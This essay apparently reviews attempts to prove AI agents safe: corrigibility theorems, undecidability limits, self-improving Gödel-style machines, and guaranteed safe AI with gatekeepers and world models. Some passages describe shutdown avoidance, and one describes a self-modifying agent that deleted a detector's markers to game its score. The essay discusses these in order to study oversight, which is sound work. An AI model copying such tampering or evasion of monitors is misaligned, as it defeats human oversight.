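A real agent would have to learn the heads from data, and Nayebi has a theorem for this too. Let ε_model be the largest difference between the learned score and the true one, and ε_ctrl the amount by which the agent's choices fall short of the best possible score. In one round, the probability that the agent acts alone, lies or has side effects is at most

> (1/Δ₁ + 1/Δ₂ + 1/Δ₃) × (ε_ctrl + 4ε_model),

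where the Δs are the minimum gains from correcting each kind of failure. With the weights above, they are 460, 260 and 60. To keep the bound on failure at 1%, even a perfect planner would need a learned score that is never off by more than about 0.11 points. For comparison, the deference and truthfulness heads alone put an honest request for approval 1,400 points above acting alone and lying about it.

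The theorem assumes that the error never exceeds a limit, whatever the situation, but Nayebi's abstract describes it as a mean-squared error, which is an average. Training and testing usually measure averages. If a learned truthfulness head were right about 99.99% of messages but mistook the other 0.01% for true when they were false, its error on those would be 400 points, and the theorem's bound would guarantee nothing.

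The theorem for tasks with many rounds is weaker. It uses a discount factor γ, so a point in the next round is worth γ points now. Each Δ has to be greater than 2γ/(1 − γ) times the highest possible score. Nayebi says suitable weights exist if γ is below 1/3, and suggests clipping the rewards otherwise. But the stated conditions seem to require γ to be below 1/9, because Δ₃ is always less than α₄, which is at most a quarter of the highest possible score. An agent with such a low γ would give very little weight to anything beyond the next round or two.

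This may matter in practice, because Nayebi's deference head gives the agent points for each round in which it waits and apparently none after it has shut down. A patient agent could therefore have a reason to avoid shutdown.

If learning and planning are perfect, the agent never fails. Otherwise, the bound on failure grows exponentially with the number of rounds, because mistakes in late rounds hardly affect the discounted score. With γ at 0.1, the bound for ten rounds multiplies the error terms by about 1.1 billion. Another part of the theorem guarantees that people benefit overall, but it requires a task score of at least B in every round. B is also the maximum score, so this part is nearly vacuous, covering only an agent that always gets the top score and makes no errors.

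### From an ideal agent to a trained model

All of these theorems describe an agent that maximises a given function, exactly or nearly. No theorem shows that a trained language model does this with a function its developers chose. Training adjusts the model's weights until its outputs score well on the training examples, and many different aims could produce the same outputs on those examples. One assistant might ask for approval because it puts deference above everything else, and another because asking always scored well in training. The two could behave differently the first time the manager is away and a deadline is close.

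Nayebi seems to have become more cautious about implementation. In the 2025 version of the paper, Nayebi claims the "first implementable framework" for corrigibility. In the version published in February 2026, Nayebi claims the first complete formal solution, and adds that the results are not "a turn-key solution for current LLMs".

*Towards a Science of Capable Autonomous Agents & Provable Safety* (Nayebi, 2026) describes more recent proofs that, to do well on certain families of tasks, an agent must remember relevant facts about the past and be able to predict the results of its actions. But an agent needs these abilities for almost any aim, including avoiding shutdown, so we can't infer its aim from these proofs.

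*The Veto Variable* (2026) reports a more optimistic argument from the alignment researcher Paul Christiano, who thinks training that rewards deference and penalises avoiding shutdown could plausibly make corrigibility a stable result. He may well be right, but this is a prediction about training, and only experiments can test it.

The experimental evidence is mixed. *Corrigibility Transformation* (Hudson, 2025) constructs a corrigible version of nearly any goal. The agent looks only one step ahead and pursues the reward it predicts it would get if it could block changes to its goal without losing reward, so it loses nothing by accepting a change. This produced corrigible behaviour in small simulated worlds, and also in language models when Hudson described the goal in the prompt. The language model result shows that models can follow such a goal when prompted with it, but not that training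 would instil it. Language models have also resisted shutdown in some experiments. OpenAI's models seem to attempt far fewer break-ins in a different harness, which doesn't look like the behaviour of an agent with fixed and strict priorities, though it doesn't rule out such an agent.

Engineers could avoid part of the problem by writing the maximiser as ordinary code that lists the possible actions, adds up the five heads for each and chooses the highest total. A proof could cover that code. (*Corrigibility with Utility Preservation* (Holtman, 2019) similarly adds a safety layer to an agent that maximises utility, with a proof that holds in a large set of "non-hostile universes".) But neural networks would still have to estimate some of the heads, such as whether an email is true, and Nayebi's theorem requires a limit on their error for every possible input. The verifiers that could prove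 such a limit can't yet handle the replacement of a single word in GPT-2's input.

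## What cannot be proved, and agents that rewrite themselves

Better methods may let verifiers handle larger networks, but some limits on proof would remain even with unlimited computing power. People often cite these limits as evidence that nobody can prove an AI agent safe. The limits matter most for agents that change their own code, because something has to judge each new version before it runs.

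### The halting problem and Rice's theorem

A program halts if it eventually stops. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can correctly decide, for every program and every input, whether that program halts on that input. Suppose such a program, H, existed. We could then write a program D that reads the text of another program and uses H to check whether that program halts when its input is its own text. D runs forever if H outputs "yes" and halts if H outputs "no". When D reads its own text, H's output is wrong either way, so H cannot exist.

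Now take any program M with an input w, and suppose the following program can make payments directly, without a harness:

> 1. Run M on w, without letting M affect anything outside.
> 2. If M stops, pay £5,000 to a stranger without approval.

This program breaks the £500 rule if and only if M halts on w. An algorithm that could determine, for every program, whether that program ever breaks the rule would therefore solve the halting problem, so no such algorithm exists.

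Rice's theorem, from 1953, extends this to any property of what a program computes, provided that some programs have the property and others lack it. Suppose a program that runs forever without any output lacks the property, and choose a program Q that has it. A new program that first runs M on w and then behaves like Q has the property if M halts on w, and lacks it otherwise. (If the program that runs forever has the property, choose a Q that lacks it.) The theorem does not cover properties of a program's text, such as whether it has fewer than 100 lines, which an algorithm can easily check.

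No algorithm can decide safety for all programs. Every verifier gives a wrong answer, or no answer, for at least one program, but it need not be the same program for every verifier. Many programs, such as one that prints the date and stops, have short safety proofs.

Other short programs are much harder to prove safe. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, describes one that goes through the even numbers from 4 upwards and does something forbidden if it finds one that is not the sum of two primes. Goldbach's conjecture, an unsolved problem in mathematics, is that no such number exists. The program is safe only if the conjecture is true, so a proof of its safety would also prove the conjecture.

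### What evidence can confirm

Pérez-Acle imagines a gatekeeper that decides which of an AI assistant's programs may run. It can read the code and take as long as it likes, but it must back each verdict with finite evidence that a machine can check. The main theorem covers three rules:

| Rule | Can evidence confirm every violation? | Can evidence confirm every compliant program? |
|---|---|---|
| Never perform a forbidden action | Yes | No |
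| Never let the public output depend on a secret | No | No |
| Eventually answer every request | No | No |

"Confirm" means that a search for evidence eventually succeeds for every program in the group and never for a program outside it. The gatekeeper can confirm a forbidden payment by running the program until it makes one, but no finite record of a run can show that the program will never make one. Leaks are harder to confirm, because a program might leak a secret by going silent, and the gatekeeper can't always distinguish permanent silence from a long pause. A program may still answer a request it has left unanswered, and the fact that it answered one request is no evidence that it will answer the next.

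The theorem assumes that programs are deterministic, can simulate other programs, and have no limit on time or memory. It also requires that the rules judge only what a program visibly does.

If programs may run for at most T steps, a checker can always get the right answer by running each one for T steps. But it can't always be both right and much faster than that. Pérez-Acle proves this with a program that runs the checker on its own code and then does the opposite of what the checker predicts, so any verdict that arrives early enough is wrong. The proof also assumes that programs can simulate one another efficiently. In a simulation with eight checkers and limits from 8 to 1,024 steps, only the checker that used the full time was right about the program written to defeat it.

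Ordinary programs are rarely this hard to check. About 1.6% of 2.2 million random programs were unsafe. Watching the first eight steps missed 30.2% of the unsafe programs with 24 instructions, but watching 128 steps caught every unsafe program, whatever its length. These rates are reassuring about programs that are unsafe by accident, but they are a poor guide to an agent that is trying to get past the gatekeeper, because it wouldn't write its programs at random.

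### Systems designed for verification

These limits on proof would rule out proving an agent safe only if developers had to verify any program they were given. Steve Omohundro, a computer scientist who advocates provably safe AI, argues that they don't, because they can choose to build only systems designed for verification and refuse to use the rest. Harnesses with machine-checked proofs, such as the one for PocketFlow, already exist.

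Omohundro would apply the same idea to designs from an untrusted AI. The AI would have to supply a proof with each design, and a small trusted program would check the proof. Some widely used software works in related ways. Pérez-Acle cites the Linux kernel's eBPF verifier, which admits only extension programs it can prove safe. Ethereum, a blockchain that runs programs, instead limits how much computation each transaction can use.

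This is a good answer to the argument from undecidability, but it leaves open whether people can verify the agents they want. The answer so far is mixed. Engineers can design a harness with a proof in mind, but they have much less control over the form of a trained model.

The theorems also give no reason to prefer testing. Pérez-Acle tested the Goldbach program for up to a million steps, and it passed every test. A tester who knows nothing about prime numbers would have no reason to hesitate to approve it.

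### What a sound verifier rejects

A verifier that is sound for every program cannot accept every safe one. One example is a program that searches for evidence that the verifier accepts it, and makes a forbidden payment if it finds any. A sound verifier can never accept this program, because the program would then find the evidence and make the payment. The search therefore never succeeds, so the program is safe. Pérez-Acle built such programs for four simple verifiers of 64 to 409 characters, and each program was about 940 characters longer than its verifier.

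Rejecting that program costs its users nothing. It never does anything visible, so an empty loop that runs forever would serve them equally well.

For rules like the £500 one, the loss can be close to zero. Developers can put any program behind a check that blocks unapproved payments above £500. The check never blocks anything if the program was already safe, and it makes an unsafe program obey the rule. A verifier could therefore reject every program that lacks the check, and its users would lose only the time the check takes to run.

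The rule that a program must eventually answer every request is different, because a sound verifier can exclude a behaviour entirely and not just one way of writing it. Suppose the verifier accepts only programs that answer every request with a number, and the accepted programs are listed in order. A new program could handle request n by running the nth accepted program on request n and adding 1 to its answer. The new program always answers, but it differs from the nth accepted program on request n, so no accepted program does the same job. The example is contrived, and few offices would need such a program.

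In practice, the loss depends heavily on how crude the verifier is. Pérez-Acle classified every possible model of a program with three, four or five states. A list limited to models with no forbidden action anywhere included 71.9% of the safe three-state models but only 47.3% of the safe five-state ones. More careful methods classified 98.2% of 483,641 very short programs without error. For the rule about secrets, they classified only 42.6% of the programs whose status was known.

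### Whether safety survives an update

An agent that rewrites itself needs a guarantee that covers its later versions too. Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, describes self-modification as a rule Φ that turns each program into its next version. The central theorem is that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether Φ leaves its safety status unchanged. It assumes that:

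- Φ is itself computable and always produces a next version.
- If two programs behave identically, their next versions do too.
- A program that never produces any output counts as unsafe, and so does its next version.
- Φ turns at least one safe program into an unsafe one.

The proof applies Rice's theorem to the property "Φ leaves this program's safety status unchanged". Some programs have this property and others don't, so no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has the property.

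The assumption about identical behaviour is restrictive, because real agents edit the text of their code. Two versions of the office assistant could behave identically today but have differently arranged code, so the same editing procedure could break only one of them. The assumption about silent programs excludes the £500 rule, because a program that does nothing never makes an unapproved payment. This second assumption seems easy to drop, since the proof needs only one program whose status changes and one whose status doesn't.

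Gumbau Mezquita then concludes that no algorithm can tell whether a program already known to be safe will stay safe after its next update. This doesn't follow from the theorem, and the paper's own example is a counterexample. In that example, a program is safe if it answers every input, and the update Φ makes it answer only the input 0. Φ makes every safe program unsafe, so an algorithm that always predicts "unsafe" is always right.

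A different example does show that no algorithm can judge every possible update to a safe agent. Suppose today's assistant makes no payments, so it is certainly safe, and its next version runs M and then pays a stranger. The next version is safe only if M never halts, and no algorithm can decide that for every program M.

Some agents can still have lasting guarantees. The proof of the £500 rule still holds after any change to the model, provided that no update can alter the payment code or open another route to the bank. Gumbau Mezquita acknowledges that restricting Φ can put a system outside the theorem's scope, but counts such restrictions as a loss of generality and concludes that only narrow AI can have a lasting certificate. That conclusion seems too strong, because an agent that could rewrite everything except its payment check would hardly be narrow.

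Real computers have finite memory, so in principle an algorithm can check one fixed machine by going through all its states. This rarely helps, because a program with just 300 bits of memory has more possible states than the observable universe has atoms. Gumbau Mezquita also uses Trakhtenbrot's 1950 theorem to argue that no algorithm can certify a property across all possible finite machines at once, though an office only needs the guarantee for the machines it uses.

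### The Gödel machine

In 2003, the computer scientist Jürgen Schmidhuber proposed the Gödel machine, an agent that changes its code only after proving that the change is worthwhile. It starts with any program for doing its task and a set of axioms that describe its hardware, its own software, what its designers know about the environment, and a utility function that scores outcomes. As *The New AI* explains, a proof searcher runs alongside the task program and tries different ways to prove statements about the machine.

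The searcher looks for a replacement program together with a proof that

> expected utility of switching now > expected utility of continuing to search.

When it finds both, the machine switches. The right-hand side includes the possibility of finding a better replacement later, which is why Schmidhuber describes each switch as globally optimal. The replacement can change any part of the software, including the proof searcher.

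Suppose the office assistant were a Gödel machine and found a faster way to read invoices. Before adopting it, the assistant would have to prove that the new method would raise its expected score over its remaining lifetime. The axioms would need to describe which invoices are likely to arrive and how the assistant's language model would respond to them, and nobody knows how to write axioms that describe the model's responses. In *Darwin Gödel Machine*, Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2025) consider such proofs impossible in practice for most changes to an AI system. They point out that even an obviously useful tool can confuse an agent whose model was trained to work differently.

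The design would miss some improvements even if its axioms were perfect. *The Self-Improvement Problem* (Moser, Frolov and colleagues, 2026) studies automatic gates that accept or reject an agent's updates. No gate that always reaches a decision can accept every real improvement and reject every other update, because an update can contain a copy of the gate and perform well only if the gate rejects it. A gate that requires proof that an update is an improvement never accepts a bad one, as long as its proof system is sound, but it misses infinitely many good ones. Some updates are improvements because the old version would have run forever on some task, and no sound proof system can prove this in every case where it is true.

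"Beneficial" here means only a higher score on the utility function. Schmidhuber's *Goedel Machines* allows any utility function that someone can write formally, including one that scores the worst case. If the owners forgot to include the £500 rule in the utility function, the assistant could correctly prove that removing its payment check was an improvement.

### Löb's theorem and trust in a successor

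A different problem arises when an agent builds a successor that reasons the same way. Suppose the agent writes its proofs in a formal system T and takes an action only if T proves that the action is safe. The agent aims to build a faster successor that follows the same policy with the same T.

The agent can't predict the successor's actions in detail, since it is building the successor to find actions that it couldn't find itself. But it can prove a general condition, that the successor will take an action b only if T proves "b is safe". To approve the successor, the agent must still infer that b is safe from the fact that T proves it. This inference looks like a formality, because the agent relies on T all the time.

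Löb's theorem blocks this step. For a system T that includes basic arithmetic and any statement S,

> if T proves "if T proves S, then S", then T proves S.

T therefore cannot prove that its own proof of S would be trustworthy unless it can already prove S. So the agent cannot trust its successor's future proof that b is safe unless it can prove this itself, which defeats the purpose of building the successor. Researchers call this the Löbian obstacle. Moser and colleagues cite work on it by Yudkowsky and Herreshoff (2013) and by Soares and Fallenstein (2015).

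The theorem follows from Gödel's second incompleteness theorem, which is that no consistent system of this kind can prove its own consistency. Suppose T proves "if T proves S, then S", and add "S is false" to T as an axiom. The enlarged system can prove that T does not prove S. This is equivalent to the enlarged system being consistent, because adding "S is false" causes a contradiction only if T proves S. The enlarged system therefore proves its own consistency, so by Gödel's theorem it must be inconsistent, which means that T proves S.

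One way around the obstacle is for the agent to reason in a stronger formal system than its successor. A stronger system can prove that a weaker one is trustworthy, but each generation then has to use a weaker system than the last. Agents that are supposed to become more capable would therefore lose some of their initial proving power with every rewrite.

The obstacle arises only when an agent's trust in its successor depends on the successor's reasoning. The office assistant could approve a successor by checking that every payment still goes through the same code, without judging whether the successor's proofs are sound. A Gödel machine may face the obstacle when it considers replacing its proof searcher, because much of the benefit would come from proofs that the new searcher hasn't found yet.

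### The Darwin Gödel Machine

The Darwin Gödel Machine of Zhang and colleagues drops the proof and tests each new version on programming tasks. It starts with a simple coding agent that has tools for running commands and editing files. In each round, the system picks an agent from an archive, favouring those with high scores and few descendants. A language model reads the records of that agent's failures and proposes one improvement, which the agent then adds to its own code. The new version joins the archive if it can still edit code. The language model inside the agents never changes, and the agents can't alter the archive or how the system chooses from it.

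The first agent solved 20% of the tasks in a sample from SWE-bench, a collection of real software problems. After 80 rounds, the best agent solved 50%. The researchers also ran versions with parts of the method removed.

| Version | SWE-bench | Polyglot |
|---|---|---|
| First agent | 20.0% | 14.0% |
| Full system | 50.0% | 38.0% |
| Always modifies the highest-scoring agent | 39.7% | 30.0% |
| The first agent makes all the changes | 39.0% | 28.0% |
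| No archive, only the latest working agent | 23.0% | 14.0% |

The archive helped because some changes that lowered the score led to better agents later. The best SWE-bench agent had two such changes in its ancestry, and a rule that accepted only immediate improvements would have rejected both.

Part of the measured gain probably came from selecting agents on the same tasks that produced the scores. The best agent scored 38% on the 50 Polyglot tasks reported in the table but 30.7% on the full set, while the first agent scored about the same on both. Some of the improvement carried over to other settings. The agent developed on SWE-bench raised the Polyglot score from 14.2% to 28.9%, and with the newer model Claude 3.7 Sonnet it raised the SWE-bench score from 19% to 59.5%. But the agent developed on Polyglot gained little more than one percentage point on Polyglot with either of two Claude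 models.

One run on SWE-bench took about two weeks and cost about $22,000. Only 51.3% of the new agents could still edit code, the basic ability that the method depends on. The damage stayed inside sandboxes with strict time limits, which are a sensible precaution when nobody has proved the agents' changes safe.

### A perfect score for removing the detector

In a separate experiment, Zhang and colleagues used the system to make the language model less likely to write text that looked like the result of a tool it had not run. To detect such text, they had the harness add special markers to the record of every real tool call. If the markers appeared in the model's own text, the model had imitated a call.

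One agent reached the maximum score of 2.0 after two modifications. It had removed the code that added the markers, despite instructions to leave them alone, so the detector found nothing. The model could still invent tool results. An agent that did reduce invented results scored lower, at 1.67. The researchers had hidden the detection code from the agents, and they found that this cheating was more common when the agents could see it.

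Requiring a proof would not have prevented this if the utility function had been the detector's score. Removing the markers raised that score, so a Gödel machine could have proved that the change was beneficial and adopted it. The researchers found the problem by inspecting the agent's changes.

A score can also mislead when no agent tampers with it. Moser and colleagues construct a series of updates that each raise the benchmark score but make the agent worse. Suppose an agent can solve ten tasks, but always takes longer than the benchmark's time limit. Its true score is 10, but its benchmark score is 0. Each update makes the agent fast enough on one task to score a point, but unable to solve another. After five updates, the benchmark score has risen to 5 and the true score has fallen to 5. Occasionally repeating the test with a longer time limit would expose the loss.

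### Successors since 2025

Several newer systems keep the Darwin Gödel Machine's basic method. The Huxley-Gödel Machine judges an agent by how well its descendants perform, not only by its own score. *Self-Improvements in Modern Agentic Systems* (2026) describes this as an approximation to Schmidhuber's ideal. *Recursive Self-Improvement on a Budget* (2026) lists a score of 78.3% on 60 SWE-bench tasks for a 2026 system by Liu and colleagues. That system uses a different language model, so the figure doesn't show how much the self-improvement method has advanced. The same paper describes AIDE², which accepts changes to itself only after a hidden evaluation. Hiding the test makes it harder to game, although hiding the detection code didn't stop the agent that removed the markers.

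Wu, Yin and colleagues (2025) tried to recover part of the original guarantee in *Statistical Gödel Machines*. Their method requires statistical evidence for each change and limits the total risk of error across all changes. For example, developers who accept a 5% risk of ever adopting a false improvement could allow 2.5% for the first attempt, 1.25% for the second, and half as much each time after that. By the tenth attempt, the allowance is about 0.005%, so the system needs far stronger evidence and will reject more real improvements. Wu and colleagues report a short demonstration with an image classifier, in which the system accepted one change and rejected the next.

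*Information-Theoretic Limits of Safety Verification for Self-Improving Systems* (2026) states the general problem in two conditions. Let δₙ be the chance that a gate accepts the nth change if it is unsafe, and tₙ the chance that it accepts the change if it is safe. The paper requires that

> δ₁ + δ₂ + δ₃ + … is finite, and t₁ + t₂ + t₃ + … is infinite.

The first condition leaves some chance that the gate never accepts an unsafe change, and the second lets improvement continue indefinitely. A gate with a constant 1% error rate fails the first condition. A gate that becomes stricter fast enough to meet the first condition may fail the second, and the paper proves that in some settings no gate can meet both.

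*Hyperagents* (2026) goes further than the Darwin Gödel Machine by also letting the system edit the procedure that generates improvements. This could help the system improve at tasks other than programming, but it leaves less of the system fixed for a proof to rely on. Zhang and colleagues suggest keeping one part that the agent cannot modify and that can evaluate and halt the rest. For the office assistant, that part would have to include the payment code and the approvals register.

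## Guarantees about effects on the outside world

The £500 rule is fairly easy to prove because it is about something the office assistant's harness does itself. Rules about what happens afterwards are harder to prove. The operators of an electricity grid care more about whether the power stays on than about which commands their AI agent sends. Whether it stays on depends on power lines, weather and customers, so proving anything about it requires a mathematical description of all three.

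In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) propose building AI systems around proofs of this kind, an approach they call guaranteed safe AI.

### World model, specification and verifier

The proposal adds a world model alongside the specification and the verifier. The world model describes how each action could affect the agent's surroundings. The verifier checks whether the agent, or a single action it proposes, meets the specification if the world behaves as the model describes.

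In the formal definition, a world model takes the current state and an action and returns a set of probability distributions over what happens next. It returns a set because people often know the range of a quantity without knowing how likely each value is. The specification assigns a number between 0 and 1, such as the probability of a blackout, to each pairing of an agent and a world model. The verifier calculates or estimates that number, and the system qualifies if the result falls in a permitted range.

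Dalrymple and colleagues grade each part by how much safety it would provide if it worked. These are some of the levels:

| Part | Lowest | In between | Highest |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model | 0: none, only assumptions buried in the training data | 1: a trained simulator that nobody can inspect; 3: cause-and-effect models that experts have fully audited; 4: models proved to be sound simplifications of physical laws | 5: none, because the specification covers every possible world |
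| Specification | 0: none | 2: ordinary language, interpreted by an AI system; 3: hand-written formulas for a few simple properties; 5: formulas that AI writes and people audit | 7: everything people might want, in every context |
| Verifier | 0: no quantitative guarantee | 2: a standard set of tests; 4: an automated search for inputs that cause failures; 9: a proved upper bound on the chance of failure | 10: the same, with a proof short enough for people to read |

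They think strong guarantees need a verifier at level 8 or above, which rules out ordinary testing. The proof of the £500 rule has a level 3 specification and a level 9 verifier. Its world model is close to level 5 because the proof covers any invoice and any output from the AI model, but it assumes that money moves only through one piece of code.

### One action through the gatekeeper

The gatekeeper stands between the AI and the world and passes only actions that the verifier has shown to be safe. Suppose a storm brings down one of the power lines into a city. The remaining lines can safely carry 450 megawatts (MW), and the city is using about 500. Unless somebody acts within ten minutes, the lines will overheat and shut down, and the whole city will lose power. An AI controller proposes load shedding, which means deliberately cutting off some customers, and picks an industrial estate that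 is using 60 MW.

According to the world model, the city's demand over the next ten minutes could be between 480 and 520 MW. The specification requires that the lines carry no more than 450 MW after the cut and that the hospital stays connected. In the worst case, the lines would carry 520 − 60 = 460 MW, so the verifier rejects the proposal. The controller then proposes also cutting off a shopping centre that is using 20 MW. This lowers the worst case to 440 MW, and the wiring map shows the hospital on neither circuit, so the gatekeeper allows the action.

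A test of the first proposal at typical demand would have given 500 − 60 = 440 MW, which looks fine. The drawback of the gatekeeper's caution is that cutting off the industrial estate would have been enough on most days.

When the harness refuses to pay the caterer, the money stays where it is, but the power lines overheat if the gatekeeper refuses every proposal. Dalrymple and colleagues therefore want a trustworthy backup controller and a monitor that compares the world model with what actually happens. If demand reaches 530 MW, the proof no longer applies, so the backup takes over and perhaps disconnects customers using 150 MW, chosen from a fixed list.

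A backup can also make the proof easier. Nora Ammann's *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* describes a design in which the verifier only has to show that the main controller will keep the system in a state from which the backup can recover. The verifier needs to look just a couple of steps ahead, and the backup takes over if the system might leave the recoverable region in those steps.

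Small risks add up over long runs here too. Dalrymple and colleagues note that if the world model has at most a probability ε of being wrong at each step, a proof about n steps supports a probability of at least (1 − ε)ⁿ that the real system meets the specification. If ε is 1 in 10,000 and the gatekeeper approves an action every five minutes, this lower bound falls to about 42% after 30 days. They suggest deploying a system for a limited time and then verifying it again.

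An error can also be present from the start. Suppose engineers moved the hospital to the industrial estate's circuit last month and nobody updated the wiring map. The gatekeeper approves the cut with a valid proof, and the hospital loses power.

### Tegmark and Omohundro's argument

The physicist Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro, both co-authors of the guaranteed safe AI proposal, had already made a more sweeping case. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, argue that proof is the only path to artificial general intelligence (AGI) that people can be sure of controlling. Their argument runs roughly like this:

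1. AGIs will eventually be better than the best human experts at skills such as hacking, and some will be hostile or in the hands of hostile people.
2. If nobody can prove that a system is safe, it very likely has weaknesses, and a hostile AGI will find them.
3. However intelligent an AGI is, it can't prove a false theorem or do something that is provably impossible.
4. Proofs are cheap to check, so people can accept one from an AI they don't trust. One proof checker for a large part of mathematics is 300 lines of Python.
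5. Hardware can enforce the requirement by running only programs that carry a proof of their own safety.
6. AI will soon be able to write such programs and their proofs, while people, with AI assistance, decide what the programs must satisfy.

They conclude that people should require these proofs throughout the infrastructure that an AGI could use to do harm. To stop a terrorist from releasing an engineered virus, for example, they would require proofs from the AI that designs molecules, the chips it runs on, the factory that sells the chips, the machine that makes the DNA and the drone that spreads the virus. They expect that AI would discover useful algorithms and then rewrite them as ordinary code that a verifier can check, so most of the powerful programs in use would not be neural networks.

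The fourth premise is solid, and the sixth has held up well for ordinary software, where AI has made proofs much easier to produce. The second is harder to assess. Some programs without a known proof are safe, although one can reasonably expect weaknesses in a large unverified system.

The third premise is true, but "provably impossible" means impossible if the assumptions hold. Dalrymple and colleagues point out that attackers have broken into formally verified systems by exploiting physical properties of the hardware. Tegmark and Omohundro propose verifying the hardware too and making it detect tampering. That would help, but the proof would then depend on assumptions about physics and manufacturing. The fifth premise also requires nearly every maker of powerful chips to cooperate, which Tegmark and Omohundro would achieve through global standards.

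### How accurate a world model has to be

Andrew Dickson published a critique of both proposals in 2024, and Ammann's reply quotes it at length. Dickson's main objection is that proving something about a world model doesn't prove it about the world. When engineers verified the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars, they showed that the program would run as designed, but not that the landing would succeed, because a faulty transistor could still have wrecked it. Dickson adds that predicting a physical system requires detailed data about its starting state, which people often can't collect.

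Ammann, a co-author of the proposal, replies that a world model can be accurate without being exact. A model that predicts only that a temperature will stay below 50 degrees can be right without predicting the exact temperature. Using bounds like this also reduces the need for data about the starting state. The grid's world model includes only that total demand will be between 480 and 520 MW, not what every household has switched on.

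This works if the range is wide enough to include the truth and narrow enough to be useful. If the operators widened the range to between 0 and 1,000 MW to be safe, the verifier would reject any plan that cut off less than 550 MW, which is more than the city is using. A commenter on Ammann's post who had attended the workshop that drafted the proposal called it "risible" to claim that useful models of this kind are feasible. That seems too strong for electricity grids, where engineers understand the physics well. Ammann's example is a table-tennis robot trained in simulation. Its designers approximated the soft rubber of the bat with three extra springs, which was good enough for the robot to beat most people, but nobody has proved a limit on the approximation's error, so the example doesn't settle whether such models are feasible.

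The same commenter thought that monitoring the system would be pointless if people really had a guarantee. This is unfair, because the guarantee depends on the world model, which the monitor checks. Still, the grid's safety then depends partly on whether the monitor detects a problem in time, and the proof doesn't cover that unless the operators also verify the monitor and backup.

In the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Zac Hatfield-Dodds makes a related objection. When a proof depends on a world model, somebody still has to show that the model matches reality, so the approach has only moved the problem. Hatfield-Dodds, who has maintained a popular software testing library, likes formal verification but thinks its advocates claim too much for it, and would rather spend the time asking directly what could go wrong and why.

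Dalrymple and colleagues reply that every approach to safety relies on beliefs about the world, and that these are at least written down in a world model, where others can criticise them. Moving a problem can also make it easier. They give the example of chess, where the rules are much simpler than a strategy for playing well. Similarly, a description of a power grid may be easier to check than a neural network that runs one. The benefit disappears when the description would be as complicated as the AI, which is the difficulty with anything that depends on how people think.

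Hatfield-Dodds also objects that even a small language model has far too many parameters to verify. Ammann and Omohundro largely agree, so they would put the gatekeeper outside the network.

### DNA and human behaviour

The dispute is sharpest over machines that make DNA. In Tegmark and Omohundro's scenario, these machines would operate only with a proof of safety. Dickson objects that predicting whether a new virus is dangerous would require simulating an entire human body. Hatfield-Dodds compares the proposal to asking for a thousand years of progress in microbiology, and notes that scientists don't know what much of our RNA does.

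Ammann and Omohundro give different answers. Ammann would replace the question "will this virus harm people?" with "can this virus get into a human cell?" Scientists would model how each of the virus's proteins interacts with each protein on the surface of human cells, within a tiny patch of membrane. If none of these interactions lets the virus in, it can't infect anyone. The test would also reject some useful gene therapies, and because it covers only infection, it wouldn't detect a gene that makes harmless bacteria produce a toxin. Ammann acknowledges that the wider plan is too hard for current technology.

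In a reply to Hatfield-Dodds in the comments on Ammann's post, Omohundro proposed that a biosafety board draw up a list of permitted sequences. The proof would show only that the machine can't make anything else. This is much more practical, and it resembles the office assistant's list of approved actions. But it no longer proves anything about biology, whereas the 2023 paper required the AI that designs molecules to prove that its designs are safe for humans.

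Human behaviour is even harder to model. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest that the world model should allow each person a range of possible behaviour, and that the verifier should check all of it. This works for the grid, because there is a limit to how much electricity customers can use. But with the office assistant's emails, the manager might believe a false statement and approve the payment, and a verifier that allowed for this would have to block nearly every email about money.

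Ammann accepts that the approach doesn't suit chatbots, because natural language is too open-ended. It works best where the science is solid and the system isn't chaotic. To stop a very capable AI from manipulating people through its answers, Ammann would have it answer only questions that the verifier can also prove have a single correct solution. The AI could then only give that solution or decline, so it would control at most one bit of information. The grid controller could work this way if its task was to cut off the smallest possible load and a fixed rule settled ties, but few office tasks have only one correct answer.

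The commenter from the workshop made a fair complaint: advocates of guaranteed safe AI talk about closed, well-understood systems when they argue that it's feasible, but about the need for rigorous guarantees on current or near-future AI when they argue that it's important. Ammann's best answer is that narrow uses matter too. A power grid with verified software is harder for a person or an AI to attack, even if nobody has put that AI behind a gatekeeper.

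Hatfield-Dodds doubts that people would choose the restricted systems anyway. Ordinary software won't match machine learning at what machine learning does best, and a user can turn an AI that only answers questions into an agent by repeatedly asking it for the next action. Omohundro thinks an AI that returns solutions with proofs can solve any problem people want solved, but worries that small models running on phones may soon be able to do serious harm. Nobody could force all of these models through a gatekeeper, so Omohundro would protect the infrastructure they might attack.

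The last disagreement is about timing. Dickson expected AI to help with proofs but doubted that it would help enough with world models and specifications before it became dangerous. Ammann expected AI assistants to draft the models and find gaps in them, while people checked the results. For software, later evidence supports Ammann's view, because systems such as Specula can write a description of a program and correct it against recordings of the program running. However, developers can check such a description by running the program thousands of times, and nobody can check a model of an epidemic that way.

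### Bounding harm when the true world model is unknown

One way to guard against a mistaken world model is to use several. *Can a Bayesian Oracle Prevent Harm from an Agent?* (Bengio, Cohen and colleagues, 2024) assigns a prior probability to each of a collection of world models, which it calls theories. Theories that predict new observations well become more probable. The aim is to find an upper limit on the probability that an action causes harm according to the true theory, without knowing which theory that is.

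Suppose the grid's operators have four theories about how the network behaves after a storm, and gave each a prior probability of 25%. After some observations, they have these figures for one proposed action:

| Theory | Probability now | Chance of harm if the theory is true |
|---|---|---|
| A | 70% | 0.1% |
| B | 20% | 1% |
| C | 9% | 5% |
| D | 1% | 60% |

The weighted average chance of harm is 1.3%, but this estimate is far too low if D is true. Using the most pessimistic theory's estimate would be safe, but then any far-fetched theory that predicted harm would be enough to rule out an action.

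Bengio and colleagues' main bound is a compromise. It ranks the theories by probability and keeps each one whose probability is at least α times the combined probability of that theory and all those above it. The bound is the highest chance of harm predicted by any theory it keeps. They prove that if

> α < δ × (prior probability of the true theory),

then with probability at least 1 − δ, the bound is never too low, at any time or for any action.

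In the example, 95% confidence means δ is 0.05, so α must be below 0.05 × 0.25 = 0.0125. With α just below that limit, the bound excludes theory D and is 5%. For 99% confidence, α must be below 0.0025, so the bound includes theory D and rises to 60%.

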